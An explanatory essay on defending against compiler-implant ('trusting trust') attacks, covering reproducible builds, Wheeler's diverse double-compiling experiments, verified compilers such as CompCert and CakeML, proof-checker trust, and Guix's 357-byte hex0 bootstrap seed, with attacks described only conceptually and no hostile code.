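Reproducible builds let several people independently build the same source code on separate machines and compare the binaries. If the binaries are identical, an attacker who controls only one of the machines cannot have altered the result. A corrupted compiler can still pass this test if everyone uses it. To expose it, the rebuilders need to check it with a second compiler that does not carry the same implant, using a procedure called diverse double-compiling (DDC).

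### Why two builds of the same source code differ

Most differences between builds have nothing to do with what the program does. Build tools often record the time. The archive format used for C libraries, for instance, includes a timestamp for each component. Some programs store the name of the folder where they were built, so a build in `/home/alice` differs from one in `/home/bob`. Two machines may also list the files in a folder in different orders, and a tool that processes them in that order will arrange the binary differently. Wheeler mentions Java compilers that sorted part of their output by values derived from memory addresses, which many systems randomise to make break-ins harder.

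Developers fix these problems one at a time. For timestamps, they have agreed on a setting, `SOURCE_DATE_EPOCH`, that gives build tools a fixed date to record instead of the current one. Reproducible Builds (2026), the monthly report of a project that works on these problems, describes a clock program whose builds began to differ in February because its sound files got a new serial number each time. The developer fixed this by switching to another audio encoder. The April report, Reproducible Builds (2026), describes Rust programs that deliberately include random bytes as a secret, to protect against an attack that overloads them. Most people download these programs already built, so an attacker can download the same file and read the secret.

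### How rebuilders compare results

Debian, a large Linux distribution, keeps a `.buildinfo` file for each package it builds, listing the exact versions of the tools used. A rebuilder installs those versions, builds the package from source code, and compares the result with the file that Debian ships. A program called `rebuilderd` automates this by monitoring a distribution's official packages and trying to reproduce them. When two files differ, a tool called `diffoscope` shows where.

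Debian has two services that test for reproducibility. One is a stress test that deliberately varies the build conditions to find packages that are sensitive to them. The other uses the `.buildinfo` files to try to reproduce the binaries Debian ships. The second test is easier to pass, but Gevers (2026), in *Re*, a message to Debian's developers, argues that it is the one that matters to users, because they want to know whether anyone can reproduce the binaries on their computers.

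In May 2026 Debian made this second test a condition of entry to "testing", the collection of packages that becomes its next release. According to Debian's *bits from the release team*, its software now blocks new packages that nobody can reproduce, as well as updates that make a reproducible package in testing unreproducible. Packages already in testing that have never been reproducible can stay, so the rule does not mean that all of Debian is reproducible. Gevers also invites developers to request exceptions.

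Nix, the package system behind NixOS, can reproduce over 90 percent of more than 80,000 packages, according to a paper by Julien Malka and Arnout Engelen that Reproducible Builds quotes. Several thousand packages could still differ when rebuilt. Arch Linux reached a smaller milestone in April 2026 with a reproducible Docker image, a ready-made copy of a basic system. To make it reproducible, the developers had to remove the keys that its package manager needs, so the package manager does not work until the user restores them.

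Software outside the distributions is reproducible much less often. Oreofe Solarin sampled 2,000 projects on the code-sharing site GitHub that came with instructions for building a Docker image. Only 56 percent produced an image, and only 2.7 percent of those images were identical when rebuilt. Changing the build settings made another 18.6 percent reproducible, leaving 78.7 percent that were not.

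### What a match proves

If an independent rebuild matches the published binary, nobody tampered with the binary between the source code and the user, unless they tampered with the rebuild in the same way. Comparing the two would have exposed the SolarWinds attack, because anyone who built the real source code on a clean machine would have got a different program. The comparison would have missed the XZ backdoor, because it was in the release archive that everyone was building from.

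This procedure would not have exposed Thompson's compiler either. In the notation used earlier, `build(S, corrupted) = corrupted` on every machine with the corrupted compiler. A thousand rebuilders who download the same compiler binary provide no more evidence about it than one. The procedure makes this more likely, because rebuilders install the same versions of the distribution's tools to match its binary, usually as ready-made binaries from the distribution. Anyone who had rebuilt NixOS from the corrupted seed in the `strip` experiment would have infected their own copy in the same way, and the copies would have matched.

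Two compilers almost never translate a large program into the same bytes, so rebuilding with a different compiler would almost always produce a different binary, whether or not one of the compilers was malicious. No general method can decide whether two different binaries do the same thing. Diverse double-compiling (DDC) avoids this problem by compiling twice.

### Diverse double-compiling

The programmer Henry Spencer suggested the idea in a short online post in 1998. Wheeler (2010) named the method and gave the first public demonstration in *Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, a paper first presented at a conference in 2005. The paper covered only compilers that compile their own source code. Wheeler's 2009 dissertation extended the method to compilers built with a different compiler.

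The method involves three compilers:

- `A` is the suspect binary, and `S_A` is its published source code.
- `P` is the parent, the compiler that supposedly built `A`, and `S_P` is the parent's source code. The parent is often just an older version of `A`.
- `T` is the second compiler. Wheeler calls it the "trusted" compiler.

If the supplier's account is true, then `A = build(S_A, P)`. The tester first repeats this step to make sure that it gives `A` again. A corrupted compiler can pass this check, as Thompson's would, but a failure shows that the tester has not yet reproduced the original conditions. Then comes DDC itself:

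```
stage1 = build(S_P, T)
stage2 = build(S_A, stage1)
```

The tester compares `stage2` with `A`, bit for bit.

Many compilers are their own parents, so `S_P` and `S_A` are the same text, which we can call `S`. Suppose one of Thompson's colleagues had suspected the C compiler in 1975 and found a second C compiler, `T`. The table uses file sizes from Russ Cox's run of Thompson's code, except for the stage 1 sizes, which are invented.

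| Step | `A` is clean | `A` is corrupted | `A` is corrupted and `T` carries the same implant |
|---|---|---|---|
| Suspect binary `A` | 10,724 bytes | 12,918 bytes | 12,918 bytes |
| First check: `build(S, A)` | Identical to `A` | Identical to `A` | Identical to `A` |
| Stage 1: `build(S, T)` | Clean compiler, 15,000 bytes | Clean compiler, 15,000 bytes | Corrupted compiler, 18,000 bytes |
| Stage 2: `build(S, stage1)` | Clean compiler, 10,724 bytes | Clean compiler, 10,724 bytes | Corrupted compiler, 12,918 bytes |
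| Is stage 2 identical to `A`? | Yes | No, so the test exposes the problem | Yes, so the test misses the implant |

The suspect compiler never runs during the two DDC stages, and its binary is used only for comparison. Thompson's implant copies itself only when the corrupted compiler compiles its own source code, and in both stages a different program compiles that source.

### Why different compilers lead to the same bits

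DDC does not require two different compilers to produce the same binary; the belief that it does is the first misconception Wheeler corrects on his page about the method. In the table, the stage 1 compiler is 15,000 bytes and the suspect is 10,724, even when both are clean, because `T` translates `S` in its own way.

Wheeler explains the point with a C program that prints the result of 2+2. Two compilers will turn it into two different binaries, but both binaries will print 4. The same reasoning applies to compilers, which are also programs. The parent `P` and the stage 1 compiler are different binaries made from the same source code, `S_P`, so they should produce the same output when given the same input, `S_A`. That output is a compiler binary, and `S_P` determines every byte of it.

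`T` can therefore be very different from the suspect. It can be much slower and even run on another type of processor. The stage 1 compiler will then run on that processor too, but the tester can instruct it to produce code for the original one.

### What Wheeler proved

Wheeler first tried to write the proofs by hand, but keeping track of the different machines involved became too laborious. He then had an automated theorem prover find them, and a separate program checked every step. His main proof shows that a match is meaningful:

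1. Assume that `T` translates `S_P` accurately. Then the stage 1 compiler does exactly what `S_P` specifies.
2. Assume that `S_P` specifies a compiler that translates `S_A` accurately. Then the stage 1 compiler does so, and stage 2 does exactly what `S_A` specifies.
3. If `A` is identical to stage 2, then `A` also does exactly what `S_A` specifies.

This proof does not depend on where `A` came from. It would hold even if a burglar had left the file on the disk.

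A second proof shows that an honest compiler will pass. If the supplier really built `A` from `S_A` with a clean parent, and certain other conditions hold, stage 2 must be identical to `A`. It follows that when the two differ, at least one of the conditions is false, but the proof does not identify which. A mismatch is not proof of an attack, either. Somebody might have added a few unused bytes to the end of a perfectly good compiler. (A third, shorter proof shows that the parent is clean if an accurate compiler built it from `S_P`.)

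The conditions are demanding in some ways and surprisingly lenient in others.

| Condition | What can go wrong otherwise |
|---|---|
| `T` understands the language of `S_P`, including any non-standard features it uses | Stage 1 fails or produces a faulty compiler |
| Nothing malicious in `T`, or in the machine it runs on, affects the translation | If `T` carries the same implant as `A`, the test misses it |
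| The compiler described by `S_P` always gives the same output for the same input | Clean compilers fail the test |
| The tester uses the original source code and build settings | Clean compilers fail the test |
| The tester gets a true copy of `A` and compares it honestly | A corrupted operating system could show the tester a clean file and run a different one |

`T` only has to compile `S_P` correctly. It could be full of bugs, and could even insert backdoors into every login program it compiles, as long as none of this affects how it compiles `S_P`. If `T` carries a different implant that does affect the result, stage 2 will probably not match `A`, and the mismatch will prompt the tester to investigate. The test will miss the corruption if `T` alters stage 1 in a way that makes stage 2 match the corrupted suspect.

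The last condition needs particular care if intruders may have controlled the computer. Wheeler suggests shutting it down and using another machine to read the suspect binary directly from its disk. He also recommends doing the test on isolated computers that have been rebuilt from trustworthy media and run nothing else.

### What a match leaves open

If a compiler passes DDC, reading its source code is enough to learn what it does, but somebody still has to read it. Wheeler gives the example of a version of Microsoft's Visual Studio that was found in 2016 to be quietly adding calls to the programs it compiled so that they sent usage data. DDC would typically not detect this, because if the instructions for adding the calls are in the compiler's source code, a binary that follows them matches its source.

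The tester also has to read the parent's source code. Suppose an attacker adds a self-copying implant to the source code of version 2 of a compiler and deletes it before version 3. The binary of version 3 is corrupted, because version 2 built it, but its source code is clean. If a tester now runs DDC on version 3 with the source code of version 2 as `S_P`, stage 1 will be malicious too. This violates the proof's second assumption, so the match won't show that version 3 is clean. Wheeler calls this a "pop-up" attack and recommends running DDC on every release before anybody uses it to build the next one, or at unpredictable times if that is impractical.

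### Choosing the second compiler

The defenders choose `T`, and can do so after the attack. To be sure of evading DDC, an attacker therefore has to guess which compilers the defenders might use and corrupt all of them, so that each inserts the right implant into the others. Wheeler considers this one of the few problems in computer security where the defender has the advantage. A later section covers whether this advantage would hold against an attacker able to corrupt many compilers at once.

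The defenders can improve their chances by choosing a `T` that shares no code or ancestry with the suspect compiler. It also helps if `T` is much older, since its makers could hardly have planned an attack on a compiler that did not yet exist. But the defenders have to be sure that their copy is old, and an old file date doesn't prove this because an attacker could have altered the file. Wheeler therefore recommends using protected original media, or several copies kept by different people.

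They could also write `T` themselves and keep it secret. This is less work than it sounds, since `T` has to compile only one program and can run slowly. Recent work may make second compilers easier to find. Reproducible Builds reports on a master's thesis by Laurent Huberdeau, who argues for using the POSIX shell, the standard command language of Unix systems, for DDC. His C compiler, `pnut`, can build itself and the Tiny C Compiler from human-readable source code using any POSIX shell. Several independent shells exist, so an attacker would have to corrupt whichever one the defenders chose.

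Defenders can also change the source code before compiling it, in ways that do not affect what it does. They might rename variables, reorder statements or translate the whole program into another language, in the hope that an implant will no longer recognise it. This would have worked against Thompson's compiler without a second compiler. His implant searched for the line `av[4] = "-P";`. A tester who reworded that line and compiled the altered source code with the corrupted compiler would have got a clean stage 1. Compiling the original source code with stage 1 would then have produced a compiler 2,194 bytes shorter than the suspect. An implant that recognised the compiler in some other way might have survived the change.

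Even defenders who trust `T` may find it too slow or too limited for daily work. More importantly, Wheeler points out that relying on `T` alone would make it the new target. If defenders use `T` only as a check, an attacker has to corrupt both compilers to stay hidden.

### Four compilers tested

Wheeler tried DDC on four compilers: the Tiny C Compiler, GCC's C compiler, and two small Lisp compilers, one of which was deliberately corrupted. All four gave the expected result in the end. For the two C compilers, most of the work was explaining differences that turned out to be harmless.

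**The Tiny C Compiler (tcc).** Wheeler first used GCC as `T` to check tcc version 0.9.22. He had built the suspect compiler himself from earlier versions, so he had good reason to think it was clean. The results did not match, and he traced this to two causes.

One was a bug in tcc. The type of processor Wheeler used has a short form of some instructions for numbers between −128 and 127, and a long form for larger ones. To decide which to use, tcc checks whether the number fits into a single byte. When tcc compiled its own source code, it translated this check wrongly, so the resulting compiler sometimes used six-byte instructions where equivalent three-byte ones would have worked. When GCC compiled the same source code, the check worked. The bug was on tcc's own list of known defects, but Wheeler found the entry only after tracking the problem down.

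The other cause was leftover data in two unused bytes. Tcc stored certain numbers in 12 bytes but set only 10 of them. When storing a zero, the copy of tcc compiled by GCC wrote eleven zero bytes followed by the value `c9`, while the copy compiled by tcc wrote twelve zero bytes. The extra bytes didn't affect how programs ran, but the difference made a bit-for-bit comparison fail.

Wheeler changed tcc's source code to avoid both problems, and the results then matched exactly. Library archives contain timestamps, so he compared the files before the tools packed them.

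Wolfgang Goerigk wrote two small compilers for a form of Lisp, one correct and one containing a trusting-trust attack. Both compiled a factorial program into the same code. Each could also reproduce itself from the correct compiler's source code, so the usual self-test did not tell them apart. But when they compiled a login program containing the text "this is the correct login", the corrupted compiler changed "correct" to "incorrect".

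With an existing Lisp system as `T`, DDC gave a result identical to the correct compiler and different from the corrupted one. Wheeler then compared his result with the corrupted compiler and found about 270 extra lines, including a copy of the login program for the compiler to recognise. A correct compiler does not need to look for a login program, so in this case the differences also revealed the purpose of the attack.

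This was the only one of Wheeler's tests with a real implant, and it was an easy test because the compilers were tiny, their output was readable, and Goerigk had not tried to disguise the attack.

**GCC.** Wheeler's largest test involved GCC's C compiler, which most Linux distributions use. He had hoped to check the copy that came with the Fedora distribution, but Fedora had not recorded enough about how it built the compiler. He couldn't do the check even with help from an engineer at Red Hat, the company behind Fedora. Instead, he built his own copy of GCC 3.0.4 and used Intel's compiler, icc, as `T`. He chose such an old version partly because icc could not easily compile several newer ones.

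Intel's compiler was a plausible choice for `T`. It and GCC came from different organisations, and Intel would have risked a copyright lawsuit by including much of GCC's code in a proprietary product. An attacker would therefore have had to break into both Intel's and GCC's systems and write a different implant for each compiler.

Wheeler again had to explain several differences. GCC stored the name of the folder in which he built it, so he had to use the same name both times. Its build instructions also used an outdated form of a common command, which made the build fail on a modern system. The hardest problem to find involved `libiberty`, a library included in GCC. According to GCC's documentation, the full build process recompiles the compiler with its new version. But because the compiled library was newer than its source code, the build program treated it as up to date and copied it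 instead of recompiling it. As a result, the finished compiler contained code produced by two different compilers.

After he corrected the build instructions, all seven files that make up the C compiler matched, including the main one, which is 6,247,750 bytes long. Getting identical files from two unrelated compilers is strong evidence that the method works on software of realistic size.

The tests are weaker evidence that the method is practical for ordinary defenders. Wheeler made the suspect binaries himself for both C compilers, and he had to give up when he tried to check one that other people had distributed. Distributions now record far more about their builds, and the rules Debian introduced in 2026 should make the same attempt easier.

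Harmless differences also create a risk, because a tester who has found innocent explanations for a dozen of them may accept the next one too quickly. A careful attacker could make an implant look like an ordinary compiler bug. Wheeler warns that showing a difference to be harmless can be extremely difficult when an adversary is involved. It is safer to change the source code or the build until the binaries match bit for bit, as he did with tcc.

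### A build tool that both sides share

The `strip` experiment raises a more serious objection: a second compiler is no help if the same corrupted `strip` processes the output of both. This is easy to see in the notation. Let `K(x)` be what comes out when `strip` processes the binary `x`, and take a compiler that is its own parent:

```
A      = K(build(S, P))
stage1 = K(build(S, T))
stage2 = K(build(S, stage1))
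```

If the compilers are clean, `build(S, P)` and `build(S, stage1)` are identical. The shared tool `K` then does the same thing to both, so `stage2` equals `A` even if `K` is corrupted. Wheeler's test of GCC had this weakness because he treated the assembler, the linker and the other supporting tools as outside the compiler. The test could have missed a similar corruption in one of them.

Wheeler had answered a more general form of this objection years before the `strip` experiment. In November 2009 the security researcher Gadi Evron wrote to him that the problem of trust could go up and down the chain forever, beyond the compiler. Wheeler replied that it was "perfectly reasonable to redefine the word 'compiler'" to include other parts of the system, even the whole operating system. This is consistent with the proof, which does not specify how many programs make up a compiler.

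To apply his answer to `strip`, the tester treats the compiler and `strip` together as the suspect, and makes sure that `T` includes an independent `strip` too. The test then goes as follows:

1. `T` and its own `strip` build both suspect tools from source code. The results are a clean compiler and a clean `strip`.
2. These two new tools build the compiler and `strip` again.
3. The tester compares both results with the distribution's copies. If the distribution's `strip` is corrupted, its copies will contain the implant and the new ones will not.

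The `strip` attack is consistent with Wheeler's proof, which assumes that nothing malicious affects the translation. When the tester runs the distribution's `strip` on the output of `T`, that `strip` becomes part of `T`, and the assumption no longer holds. But the proof doesn't identify tools that testers have overlooked. If both sides use an overlooked tool that can alter binaries, any malicious change it makes will appear in both results, as with `strip`, and comparing them won't reveal it.

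### The price of a wider definition

Widening the definition makes the test more work. Wheeler's three requirements are the source code of every component, a separate trusted compiler that can compile all of it, and time to make it work. This is manageable for `strip` alone, but the seed and standard build steps of NixOS involve dozens of tools. A tester who wants to rule out all of them needs independent replacements for the first stage, and each replacement must behave enough like the original for the build to succeed.

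The operating system is even harder to check. It can alter any file that the tools read or write, so a cautious tester would test it too, and would run the first stage on a different operating system. Every added component brings its own timestamps, folder names and obscure bugs, any of which can cause a mismatch that the tester has to explain. Wheeler and a colleague failed many times before they succeeded with GCC's C compiler alone. In 2009 Wheeler listed recompiling an entire operating system as future work.

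Not every user has to run DDC. Wheeler suggests that organisations could run it on important compilers and publish the checksums of the binaries that passed, along with those of the source code. Users would then only have to compare checksums. They would be trusting the organisation, but several organisations could test the same compiler with different choices of `T`, and anyone with the source code could repeat the test.

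Evron was not entirely persuaded by the wider definition, and objected that the process was endless because the tester now had to trust the second system. Wheeler had already accepted that people must eventually treat some set of components as trustworthy enough, but he denied that this was blind faith. He is right on this narrower point, because one corrupted system is enough to deceive its users before the test, whereas after a match the attacker must also have corrupted the second system in a way that leads to exactly the same bits.

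## Can a mathematical proof tie a binary to its source?

CakeML, a compiler for a language called ML, has a machine-checked proof that ties the compiler's exact bytes to its source. Anyone who relies on the proof no longer has to trust an older compiler, but does have to trust the program that checked the proof and a mathematical model of the processor.

Most proofs about compilers concern the algorithm a compiler uses to translate programs, not whether its binary matches its source code. Thompson's attack changed only the compiler's binary and left the algorithm in its source code intact, so such a proof does not rule it out.

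### CompCert: a proof about the algorithm

CompCert is a compiler for most of C. Its developers wrote it mainly in Coq, a proof assistant, which is software for writing programs and proofs about them and checking every step of the proofs. They proved that if CompCert compiles a C program that does nothing the rules of C leave undefined, the resulting assembly code behaves as the source code specifies.

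Coq translates CompCert's verified code into OCaml, an ordinary programming language, and the OCaml compiler then produces the binary that people use. *The Trusted Computing Base of the CompCert Verified Compiler* (Monniaux and Boulmé, 2022) examines the whole process for steps that the proof leaves out.

| Step | Does the proof cover it? |
|---|---|
| Coq translates CompCert into OCaml | No |
| The OCaml compiler builds CompCert's binary | No |
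| CompCert simplifies the C program it has received | No |
| CompCert translates the simplified program into assembly instructions | Yes |
| CompCert expands some instructions and prints them all as text | No |
| Another toolchain, such as GCC's, assembles and links the result | No |

A corrupted OCaml compiler could recognise CompCert and add a backdoor to it, and the proof would still be valid. *Simple, Light, Yet Formally Verified, Global Common Subexpression Elimination* (2021) considers a harmful bug in OCaml unlikely, because it would have to make CompCert silently produce wrong code while going unnoticed in every other OCaml program. This is a good argument about accidental bugs, but Thompson deliberately designed his implant to behave this way.

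Bugs have occurred in the later steps. Monniaux and Boulmé describe one in the unproved code for copying blocks of memory, which made CompCert produce wrong programs for four types of processor without warning. In a modified version of CompCert, the printing step wrote "and" where the verified part had produced "nand", the opposite operation.

Some of these gaps are closing. For certain processors, the company that sells CompCert also offers a tool that compares the compiler's assembly code with the finished binary. *Misquoted No More* (2026) lists a verified compiler from Coq's language to an intermediate form of OCaml, but the rest of the OCaml compiler would still have to process the result.

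### CakeML: a proof about the bytes

CakeML's developers avoid the unproved translation by running their compiler inside a proof assistant, HOL4, which proves what a program's result is by running it. For example, if `double(n)` is defined as `n + n`, HOL4 evaluates `double(3)` by replacing it with `3 + 3` and then with `6`, checking each replacement as a step in a proof. The result is the theorem `double(3) = 6`. Running a compiler takes vastly more steps but works the same way.

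Let `compile` be the compiler as a mathematical function, `S` its source code, and `M` a list of bytes. The argument has three parts:

1. For every valid program `p`, the machine code `compile(p)` behaves as `p` does.
2. The program `S` carries out the function `compile`.
3. `compile(S) = M`.

The bytes `M` therefore carry out `compile`. One exception is that the machine code may stop early if it runs out of memory (Myreen, 2021, *The CakeML Project's Quest for Ever Stronger Correctness Theorems*).

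*Self-compilation and self-verification* (Kumar, 2016) applies this to Thompson's attack. The attack needs a corrupted compiler binary to translate the new compiler's source code, but here HOL4 calculates the translation. An attacker would have to corrupt HOL4 so that it recognised this calculation or substituted other bytes when it saved the result. That is still possible, because the CakeML developers build HOL4 with Poly/ML, an ordinary compiler.

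The calculation inside HOL4 serves the same purpose as the second compiler in DDC, but the proof also covers malicious instructions in the compiler's source code, which DDC would not detect. Part 1 of the CakeML proof rules out a compiler that adds a second password to a login program, because the altered program would not behave as its source code specifies.

The bytes also have to get from the theorem into a file that a computer can run. Kumar did this with a C program of about 30 lines, which he compiled with ordinary unverified tools. Those tools could have altered the bytes. Because the theorem contains `M` in full, a defender can compare `M` with the bytes in the finished file. However, the proof does not cover the code that loads those bytes.

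### Comparing source and binary as numbers

*Certified Compilation based on Gödel Numbers* (Silva and Pereira, 2025) describes a way to check a compiled program against its source code without a proof assistant or a second compiler. The paper's compiler, Charon, turns each construct in the source code into a fixed pattern of instructions. One procedure computes a number from the source code, and another computes a number from the compiled program. If the compiler translated the source faithfully, the two numbers are equal.

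The method comes from the logician Kurt Gödel. Each symbol has a code and each position has a prime number: 2 for the first position, 3 for the second, 5 for the third, and so on. To encode an expression, raise each prime to the code of the symbol in that position, then multiply. If `a` has the code 4, `+` has 3 and `b` has 7, then `a + b` becomes:

```
2^4 × 3^3 × 5^7 = 16 × 27 × 78,125 = 33,750,000
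```

A whole number factors into primes in only one way, so anyone can recover the three symbols and their order from 33,750,000. The expression `b + a` gives a different number, 2,160,000.

Silva and Pereira's smallest example is what many people consider the shortest valid C program, which does little more than return. Its number is `2^2 × 3^19 × 5^113`, which has 89 digits. The factor for the return statement arises twice:

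1. In the source code, the return statement is the second construct and has the code 19, so it contributes `3^19`.
2. In the compiled program, a return takes two instructions. `MOV` puts the result in the agreed place, and `JR` jumps back to whatever called the program. The second procedure recognises this pair as a return, and also records `3^19`.

The other two factors match in the same way. Now suppose that a corrupted compiler inserts another operation, with some code `k`, just before the return. The compiled program's number becomes `2^2 × 3^k × 5^19 × 7^113`, which no longer equals the number for the source code. (The full table of codes later in the paper gives a return statement 41 instead of 19. Either works, as long as both procedures use the same table.)

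A third party needs only the source code, the compiled program and the encoding rules to check the match. The rules are simple enough that checkers could implement them independently, or work through a tiny program by hand. Silva and Pereira sketch proofs that faithful compilation always gives the source and compiled program equal numbers, and that two different compiled programs never have the same number.

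Charon handles a subset of C with conditions, loops, non-recursive functions, arrays and two sizes of integer, but without pointer arithmetic. This is enough for FaCT, a small language for cryptographic code. The numbers grow exponentially with the length of the program, so Charon stores them as lists of factors, which grow only linearly. In tests on 20 small programs, encoding the source code took at most about 1.6 milliseconds, and encoding the compiled program was usually faster. The greater drawback is that the compiled programs run more slowly, because the compiler cannot optimise them without breaking the match between source and binary.

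The method is still far from checking a real compiler, which would normally need recursion and many other features that Charon lacks. It also doesn't check a finished binary. Charon's output resembles code for RISC-V, an openly published processor design, but it assumes an unlimited number of registers, the small storage slots inside a processor. A real processor has a fixed number, and Silva and Pereira acknowledge that assigning values to them would break the match. They leave testing against an attacker who forges encodings to future work. A program has to calculate the numbers, and a corrupted one could report a false match, so their claim that the method needs no trusted verifier is too strong.

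### What checks the proof?

Proof assistants have bugs too. Monniaux and Boulmé cite an average of one critical bug a year in Coq. One bug let users prove a false statement if they defined a type with more than 255 alternatives. Any statement can be proved from a false one, including that a corrupted binary matches its source. Monniaux and Boulmé think it highly unlikely that CompCert's developers accidentally relied on such a bug, but an attacker would look for one. *Developments in Formal Proofs* (2014) describes a weakness in another proof assistant, HOL Light. The version written in OCaml let users change what a theorem stated after proving it.

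Defenders can reduce this risk by separating the search for a proof from the checking. Finding a proof may take years of work and a lot of software, but checking it only requires confirming that each step follows from earlier ones by one of a few fixed rules. Defenders therefore don't have to trust whoever wrote the proof, even if it was an AI system.

Metamath Zero uses two files. A person reads the first, which contains the axioms and the statements to prove. The second contains the proofs, and a small program called the verifier checks them against the first. *Metamath Zero* (Carneiro, 2019) treats the proof file as if a malicious stranger had sent it.

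The verifier is small. A program like it uses only about 25 kinds of processor instruction, while the manual for that processor family runs to some 3,000 pages. *Carnap Ten Years Later* (2026), which uses a newer verifier for the same system, describes the trusted part as "small enough to fit in one person's head".

Simple rules also make it easier to write several checkers independently. Carneiro counted 17 checkers, written in almost as many programming languages, for Metamath, the older system on which Metamath Zero is based. To get a false proof past all of them, an attacker would need a flaw or an implant in every one. Testing the checkers with faulty proofs would expose one that accepts everything, but not one that wrongly accepts only the attacker's proof.

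Running seventeen checkers on one corrupted operating system is little better than running one, so defenders should also repeat the check on different machines, preferably ones with different types of processor. This is practical because checking can be very fast. Carneiro's verifier checked a library of more than 34,000 proofs in about 0.2 seconds. A computer a thousand times slower would take a little over three minutes, if it had enough memory.

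CakeML's proof is much harder to check this way. Kumar writes that HOL4 can in theory export its proofs for other programs to check, but that the calculations inside the logic make those proofs extremely large. Defenders could instead repeat the whole calculation on another machine and compare the bytes, but the CakeML developers warn that a full build "requires significant resources", and both machines would still be using HOL4. A longer-term solution is to run the proof assistant on verified software as well. In *Cakes That Bake Cakes*, Sewell, Myreen and colleagues (2023) built what they believe is the first verified run-time environment that can support a proof assistant of the usual design, in which only a small kernel can create theorems.

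### What people still have to trust

Carneiro wanted the proof checker Metamath Zero to verify its own binary. By 2019 he had written the statement to prove and a model of the processor, but not the proof. A finished proof would be good evidence against accidental errors, but Kumar points out that a faulty checker might wrongly approve itself. Carneiro's statement would also be true of a checker that rejected everything, so users also have to see Metamath Zero accept a proof. To guard against a deliberate implant, they would still need other checkers or a direct inspection of the binary.

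A proof about machine code depends on a mathematical description of what each instruction does. Kumar's model covers only some of the instructions available to ordinary programs. It also leaves out virtual memory, which gives each program its own view of the computer's memory, and assumes that input and output work. CakeML's developers have since extended their proofs to the circuit description of Silver, a small processor they designed. The theorem does not apply if the manufactured chip contains a hardware Trojan.

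An attacker who can alter the statement being proved does not need to forge a proof. Suppose somebody changes the definition of "behaves as the source code specifies" so that it excludes what a login program does with one particular password. A backdoor that uses this password would then be consistent with the theorem, and every correct proof checker would accept the proof. People therefore have to read the definitions, including those of the programming language and the processor. Carneiro keeps the statements in a separate file from the proofs, partly so that changes to them stand out. He also assumes that the computer displays this file accurately, which a corrupted operating system might not do.

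## Can software be rebuilt from a seed small enough to read?

Most of the software on a Linux system can be rebuilt from a seed small enough to read. Since 2023 the Linux distribution Guix has built its packages from a 357-byte program, which one person could probably check by hand in a day. The build still needs a running kernel (the core of an operating system) and a 25 MiB helper program, neither of which is built from the seed. Another project, live-bootstrap, starts without an operating system and builds its own kernels, but still depends on the machine's firmware and on a second computer to prepare the disk.

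DDC and proofs both check an existing compiler. Bootstrapping builds a new one without using any existing compiler, so an implant that passes from one compiler to the next cannot reach it.

### Why a build needs a seed

Building GCC requires a working compiler, an assembler, a linker, a shell and dozens of small utilities. A distribution normally starts with ready-made copies of all these. *The Full-Source Bootstrap*, a section of the Guix manual, puts the traditional set at about 250 MB and says inspecting it is "next to impossible". GNU's *Stage0* compares it to 250,000 pages full of numbers. Someone who spent five seconds on each byte would need nearly 200 working years just to look at them all once. The NixOS seed that Malka and colleagues corrupted was a collection of this kind.

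Jeremiah Orians wrote the 357-byte seed program that replaced most of Guix's bootstrap binaries. Jan Nieuwenhuizen, the developer of GNU Mes, learned of it in 2016 and spent years connecting it to the rest of Guix. In January 2021, his *wip-full-source-bootstrap* presented the first working version, which built a "hello" program in Guix from that seed. Guix adopted the method for everyone two years later. More than 22,000 packages were then built up from the seed, according to *The Full-Source Bootstrap*, which Nieuwenhuizen wrote under his nickname, Janneke.

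### How two typed digits become one byte

The seed is a program called hex0. It reads a text file of hexadecimal digits, ignores spaces and comments, and writes one byte for each pair of digits. Hexadecimal is base 16 and uses the letters A to F for the values 10 to 15.

One line of hex0's own source code contains the digits `58`, followed by a comment. This is what happens to them:

1. The text file stores each typed character as a number. The character `5` is 53, and `8` is 56.
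2. Hex0 checks that each number lies in the range for the characters `0` to `9`, and subtracts 48, the number for `0`. This gives 5 and 8.
3. It multiplies the first by 16 and adds the second: 5 × 16 + 8 = 88.
4. It writes a single byte with the value 88, or `01011000` in binary.

On the x86 processors used in most PCs, this byte is an instruction to take the top value off the stack, a list in memory, and put it in a register named EAX. Hex0 converts digits to bytes regardless of what the bytes mean, so it would convert the digits of a photograph in the same way.

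Pairs of hexadecimal digits correspond one-to-one with bytes, so anyone can write out the 357-byte binary as 714 digits or recover the binary from those digits. The source code adds only comments and spacing. By contrast, nobody can recover the original text of a C program from its binary. Because the 357-byte binary can be converted to digits and back, Guix's developers say that they can "bless" it as source code.

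The comments are useful, but they don't prove what the code does. A malicious author could write "check if we are done" beside an instruction that does something else, so a careful reader has to look up the digits in the processor's manual.

Comparing the 714 digits with the listing would take about half an hour, at five seconds a byte. The first 84 bytes are a header that Linux uses to load the program, and the other 273 are instructions, probably between 100 and 140 of them. At three minutes each, working out what the instructions do would take five to seven hours. Someone who already reads assembly language could finish in a working day, while a beginner might need a week or two. These are rough estimates, but one person could still do the work even if they are ten times too low.

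Hex0 can compile its own source code, so a corrupted copy could in principle reproduce itself as Thompson's compiler did. But hex0 can also be built without an existing copy, using one line of standard Unix commands in which `sed` deletes the comments from the source and `xxd` turns the digits into bytes. In *Verifying and documenting live-bootstrap*, Faase converted the same source with a program written in Brainfuck, a language with only eight commands, and got a file identical to hex0. He also wrote his own emulator for the few x86 instructions that the early tools use, partly to confirm that these tools read no hidden binaries.

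All these checks run on computers that might themselves be corrupted. One way to avoid this is to build hex0 as a circuit. According to Guix's *IRC channel logs* (2026), Orians pointed in April 2026 to a project called Steadyhand that appeared to have done so, with buttons to write a byte and to jump to what the user had entered.

### From hex0 to a C compiler

Writing a large program in hex0 would be tedious, so each new tool removes one kind of drudgery and provides a slightly more convenient language for writing the next tool.

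| Tool | Language of its source code | What it adds |
|---|---|---|
| hex0 | hex0 | Turns pairs of digits into bytes |
| hex1 | hex0 | One-letter labels for places in the program |
| hex2 | hex1 | Labels of any length, and more kinds of address |
| M0 | hex2 | Names for instructions |
| cc_x86 | M0 | A compiler for a small part of C |
| M2-Planet | The part of C that cc_x86 accepts | A compiler for a larger part of C, for six types of processor |
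| M1 | C | A better version of M0 that works for all six |
| Mes | C | An interpreter for the language Scheme |
| MesCC | Scheme | A C compiler good enough to build the Tiny C Compiler |
| Tiny C Compiler | C | Nearly all of standard C, and much faster compiling |
| Old GCC | C | A full compiler for C, and later for C++ |
| Modern GCC | C++ | The compiler that current software expects |

Askayo, Štikonas and colleagues, in *parts.rst*, document the steps in live-bootstrap, which uses the same early tools as Guix. They illustrate the first four languages with a short loop. One of its instructions leaves the loop when there is nothing more to do:

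```
hex0    74 14
hex1    0F84 %b
hex2    74 !loop_options_done
M0      je %loop_options_done
```

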